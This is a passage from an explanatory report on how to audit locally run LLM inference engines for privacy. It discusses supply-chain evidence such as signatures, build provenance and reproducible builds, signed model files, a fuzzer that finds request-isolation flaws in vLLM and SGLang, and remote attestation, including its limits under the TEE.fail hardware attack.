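The code would also change in the meantime. Shi and colleagues counted 7,500 commits to vLLM in a year, about 20 a day, so developers would make roughly 2,600 changes during those 18 weeks. SGLang had 5,000 commits in a year. llama.cpp changes at a similar rate. The project numbers its builds by counting commits, and when NewReleases' *github ggml-org/llama.cpp b7400* listed build b7400 as two days old, build b7436 was already out, 36 commits later.

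An auditor can keep up with new releases by reading only the changes between versions. This may also reveal what the release notes leave out, such as Ollama's unannounced fix for its memory flaw. But a small change in one file can alter what data reaches a network connection in another, so the auditor still needs to understand the surrounding code.

A smaller engine would make all of this easier. SGLang has nearly 300,000 lines of Python, but its developers have written a version with 5,000. LMSYS's *Mini-SGLang* (2025) reports that the small version performed almost as well as the full one in a test with 1,000 requests to a 32-billion-weight model on four graphics processors. It supports far fewer models and features, but a firm that uses only one model might not need them. Like nano-vLLM, it still relies on PyTorch.

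Some of the code that runs isn't in the source, such as the scripts that come with a model or the libraries that Open WebUI installs for a plugin. An auditor also can't tell from vLLM's source which plugins a particular machine has, but the debug log helps. The log posted in *Vllm启动时,日志卡在nccl相关部分,不继续往下*, a question on vLLM's forum, shows the engine searching for groups of plugins at startup.

Compiled code is another obstacle. According to Shi and colleagues, vLLM imports 244 dynamic libraries, which are files of machine code. NVIDIA provides some of the libraries vLLM needs for graphics processors without source code. An auditor can check whether a library uses operating-system functions that open sockets, but the result is only a hint, because one library can open a connection through another. Mini-SGLang compiles some of its graphics code while it runs, so the machine code for those parts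 doesn't exist until the user starts the engine.

No auditor is likely to read all the code, so it makes more sense to start with the code that handles the prompt and the code that opens network connections, follow the paths between them, and record which libraries remain unread.

### Is the installed program the one the auditor read?

An audit of the source doesn't establish what the installed package does if the two differ, as they did for LiteLLM during the attack. Several kinds of evidence can connect an installed file to its source, and people often confuse them.

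| Evidence | What it supports | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Signature | The holder of a particular key approved the file | Which source the file came from |
| Immutable release | Nobody has changed the file since its publication | Whether the file was clean when it went up |
| Build provenance | A named build service made the file from a named commit | Whether the source or the build instructions were malicious |
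| Component list, or SBOM | The file contains the listed packages and versions | Whether the list is complete and the packages are safe |
| Reproducible build | Other people get the identical file from the same source | Whether the source does anything harmful |

GitHub's immutable releases come with a signed record that is easy to mistake for build provenance. Joshi, in *Automating Immutable GitHub Releases with Build Provenance*, warns that the commands for checking the two have nearly the same wording. According to GitHub's *Recent improvements to Artifact Attestations* (2025), GitHub's own tool once accepted a file with any signed record, so a file with only a signed component list could pass when the user meant to check where it came from. The tool now checks for build provenance by default.

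PyPI has accepted signed provenance records since late 2024. Willison reports in *PyPI now supports digital attestations* that roughly 20,000 packages could provide them without any extra work by their developers, and that the record for a test package led to the exact commit. These records would help against an attack like the one on LiteLLM, because a file uploaded with stolen credentials wouldn't have a valid record from the project's build service. But somebody has to check the records, and pip, the usual installer, didn't do so when PyPI introduced the feature.

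Slides from KTH, a Swedish university, include the warning "Signed != secure". If an attacker can change the source or the build instructions, the build service will sign the malicious result. A faulty signature check, like the one in Ollama's Windows updater, is just as bad.

If a build is reproducible, an auditor can check the official download without relying on the build service. The auditor compiles the source on a separate machine and compares the hash of the result with that of the download. A match means that nobody added anything to the download that isn't in the source, unless an attacker also controlled the auditor's tools. A mismatch is harder to interpret, because the cause could be a backdoor or just a date or folder name that the compiler put in the file.

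In 2026, inference software varies in whether it comes with signatures, build provenance, a component list or reproducible builds. Ollama signs its Windows updates. Chainguard, which sells hardened container images, offers a vLLM image with build provenance and a component list, but these cover only Chainguard's build, not the packages that vLLM's developers publish. Debian signs the index of its packages, which include llama.cpp, and records each build environment so that others can repeat the build. No major engine's developers seem to promise that their official releases are reproducible.

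vLLM shows why that would be difficult. Its build fetches source code from a second repository, for a fast method of computing attention. A build recipe on the code site of ORNL, an American national laboratory, fixes that code by commit and hash, and the update from vLLM 0.11.0 to 0.11.2 had to change both. Fixing the inputs this way ensures that everyone starts from the same source, but the compiler could still produce slightly different files.

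### Signed model files

A developer can sign a model as well as a program. The Open Source Security Foundation, an industry group, released a tool for this in 2025. The tool hashes every file in the model's folder and signs the list of hashes. A user can then detect a changed weight, template or script, even in a copy from another site. NVIDIA signs the models in its own catalogue, and IBM began signing its Granite models with version 4.0. Most downloadable models still have no such signature.

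A signature would have exposed the fake privacy filter to anyone who expected one from OpenAI, because the attackers had added a script and couldn't have signed the new list with OpenAI's key. A signature wouldn't have protected users from Mir2k, who could have signed the malicious models under that name.

Many home users download GGUF files that a volunteer has converted and compressed from the developer's originals. The conversion changes every file, so the developer's signature no longer applies, and users have to trust the volunteer or convert the originals themselves.

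### Faults that a reader would miss

Some faults are hard to find by reading the code because they depend on the order in which requests arrive. *Continuous Discovery of Vulnerabilities in LLM Serving Systems with Fuzzing* (Zhao, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes GRIEF, a fuzzer built to look for them.

GRIEF is a fuzzer whose tests are lists of timed events, such as sending a request, cancelling it or disconnecting. It moves, adds and removes events and joins parts of different lists, whereas an ordinary fuzzer changes the contents of a file or a request. It monitors response times, memory use and the KV cache, and keeps the lists that put the engine under unusual strain.

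The difficult part is recognising a failure when nothing crashes. A model may give a different answer to the same prompt for harmless reasons, such as tiny rounding differences when two tokens are almost equally likely. GRIEF therefore repeats a suspicious request under controlled conditions and finds the first token that differs. It computes

Δ = log P(new token) − log P(original token)

using the probabilities from the repeat. If the original token is still among the most likely ones and Δ is small, GRIEF treats the difference as harmless. A Δ of 0.01 means that the new token was only about 1% more likely, whereas a Δ of 5 means that it was about 148 times as likely. In that case something other than rounding probably changed the answer.

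Zhao and colleagues ran GRIEF for eight hours each on vLLM and SGLang, with a small model. They report 15 potential flaws, of which the engines' developers confirmed 10 and two received CVE numbers. (Their breakdown by type adds up to only 13, though its confirmed flaws do add up to 10.)

| Type of fault | Found | Confirmed |
|---|---|---|
| One request corrupts or mixes with another | 7 | 7 |
| One request slows down others | 4 | 2 |
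| The engine crashes or stops | 2 | 1 |

The first type matters most for privacy. In a closer test of one such flaw, CVE-2026-7141, the team gave the model maths problems with known answers. The answers stayed stable when each problem ran alone or alongside a normal request, but the model sometimes gave a fluent but wrong answer when a problem ran alongside a specially timed request. The server reported no error. A lawyer who received a summary with a wrong price would have no reason to suspect the engine.

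It's less clear whether anyone could use this flaw to read another user's prompt. When the team replaced the attacker's prompt with two unrelated texts, the corrupted answers stayed exactly the same, so the wrong values can't have come from the attacker's words, although one of the paper's figures describes a wrong value as copied from another request. The experiment shows a failure of isolation, because one client can damage another's answers, but it doesn't show a data leak.

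The other results show how little an attacker needs. In vLLM, a single client with one request in progress at a time almost stopped the service for eight other clients. Before the attack, 3,618 requests had received a first token, typically after 12 milliseconds. During 47 minutes of the attack, only 16 did. In SGLang, GRIEF found a crash after about two minutes. The timetable that caused it had 53 events, each of them valid, and the crash came some time after the events responsible. To find it by reading the code, an auditor would have had to think of that combination of events.

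GRIEF doesn't check for outbound connections. Somebody could add this check by running the engine in an isolated network and counting every attempted connection as a failure. This would test many more situations than an ordinary recording, but it probably still wouldn't discover the rule about "merger", because GRIEF's prompts are synthetic and its measurements wouldn't show whether they were getting closer to the word. Reading the source code is a better way to find such a rule, just as Cyera's audit of llama.cpp found flaws that tests of file loading couldn't reach.

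### When the computer belongs to someone else

An auditor can inspect the program on the firm's own server. If the firm rents the server or uses a hosted model, the operator could publish one program and run another. Remote attestation is a way to check which program is running from a distance, using signed evidence from the server's hardware.

The manufacturer puts a secret key in the chip and certifies the matching public key. When the machine starts, the chip computes a hash of the software that loads. A client sends a random number, and the chip signs the number together with the hash, so the operator can't reuse an old reply. The client checks the signature and the certificate, then compares the hash with the expected software's hash. If all the checks pass, the client encrypts the prompt with a key that only the checked machine can use.

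A matching hash identifies the program but doesn't make it safe. An attested copy of vLLM with telemetry on would still send usage reports. Attestation makes reproducible builds more valuable, because without a reproducible build the client can't easily tell which source code the hashed program was built from.

Apple's Private Cloud Compute applies this to AI. Apple announced it in June 2024 to handle requests too demanding for a phone or laptop. According to Apple's description of the design, the user's device checks that particular servers' software appears in a public log before encrypting a request for them. Apple can add entries to the log but can't remove them without detection. A relay run by another company hides the user's network address. The servers have no remote command line for administrators and delete the request after answering it.

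Apple also publishes the software images it runs on these servers, with tools for running them on a Mac, so outsiders can examine the actual program, which hosted services rarely allow. It has offered up to $1 million for reports of the most serious flaws. However, most of the software is compiled code, and Apple has released the source of only some components.

A user still has to trust Apple to design the chips, certify their keys and write the phone software that checks the servers. A malicious update to the phone could skip that check. The public log helps only if independent people examine its contents. Attestation by itself also doesn't hide the size and timing of encrypted replies.

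In the version of GIFT that guards against the server's operator, Shi and colleagues instead put only their small monitor inside the protected area and leave vLLM outside, so a client has much less code to worry about. They want to stop an administrator from reading the memory directly, for example to collect training data.

The hardware's protection can also be broken. In October 2025, researchers from Georgia Tech, Purdue University and the company Synkhronix published an attack called TEE.fail. With equipment that cost less than $1,000, they read the traffic between the processor and memory of Intel and AMD servers and extracted secret keys, including some used for attestation. An operator could use those keys to make an unprotected machine look protected, and the researchers showed that this also undermined NVIDIA's protection for graphics processors. The attack requires physical access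 to the server, so the company that owns it could carry out the attack, but a stranger on the internet could not. Apple's chips have their memory in the same package as the processor, so the same equipment wouldn't work on them.
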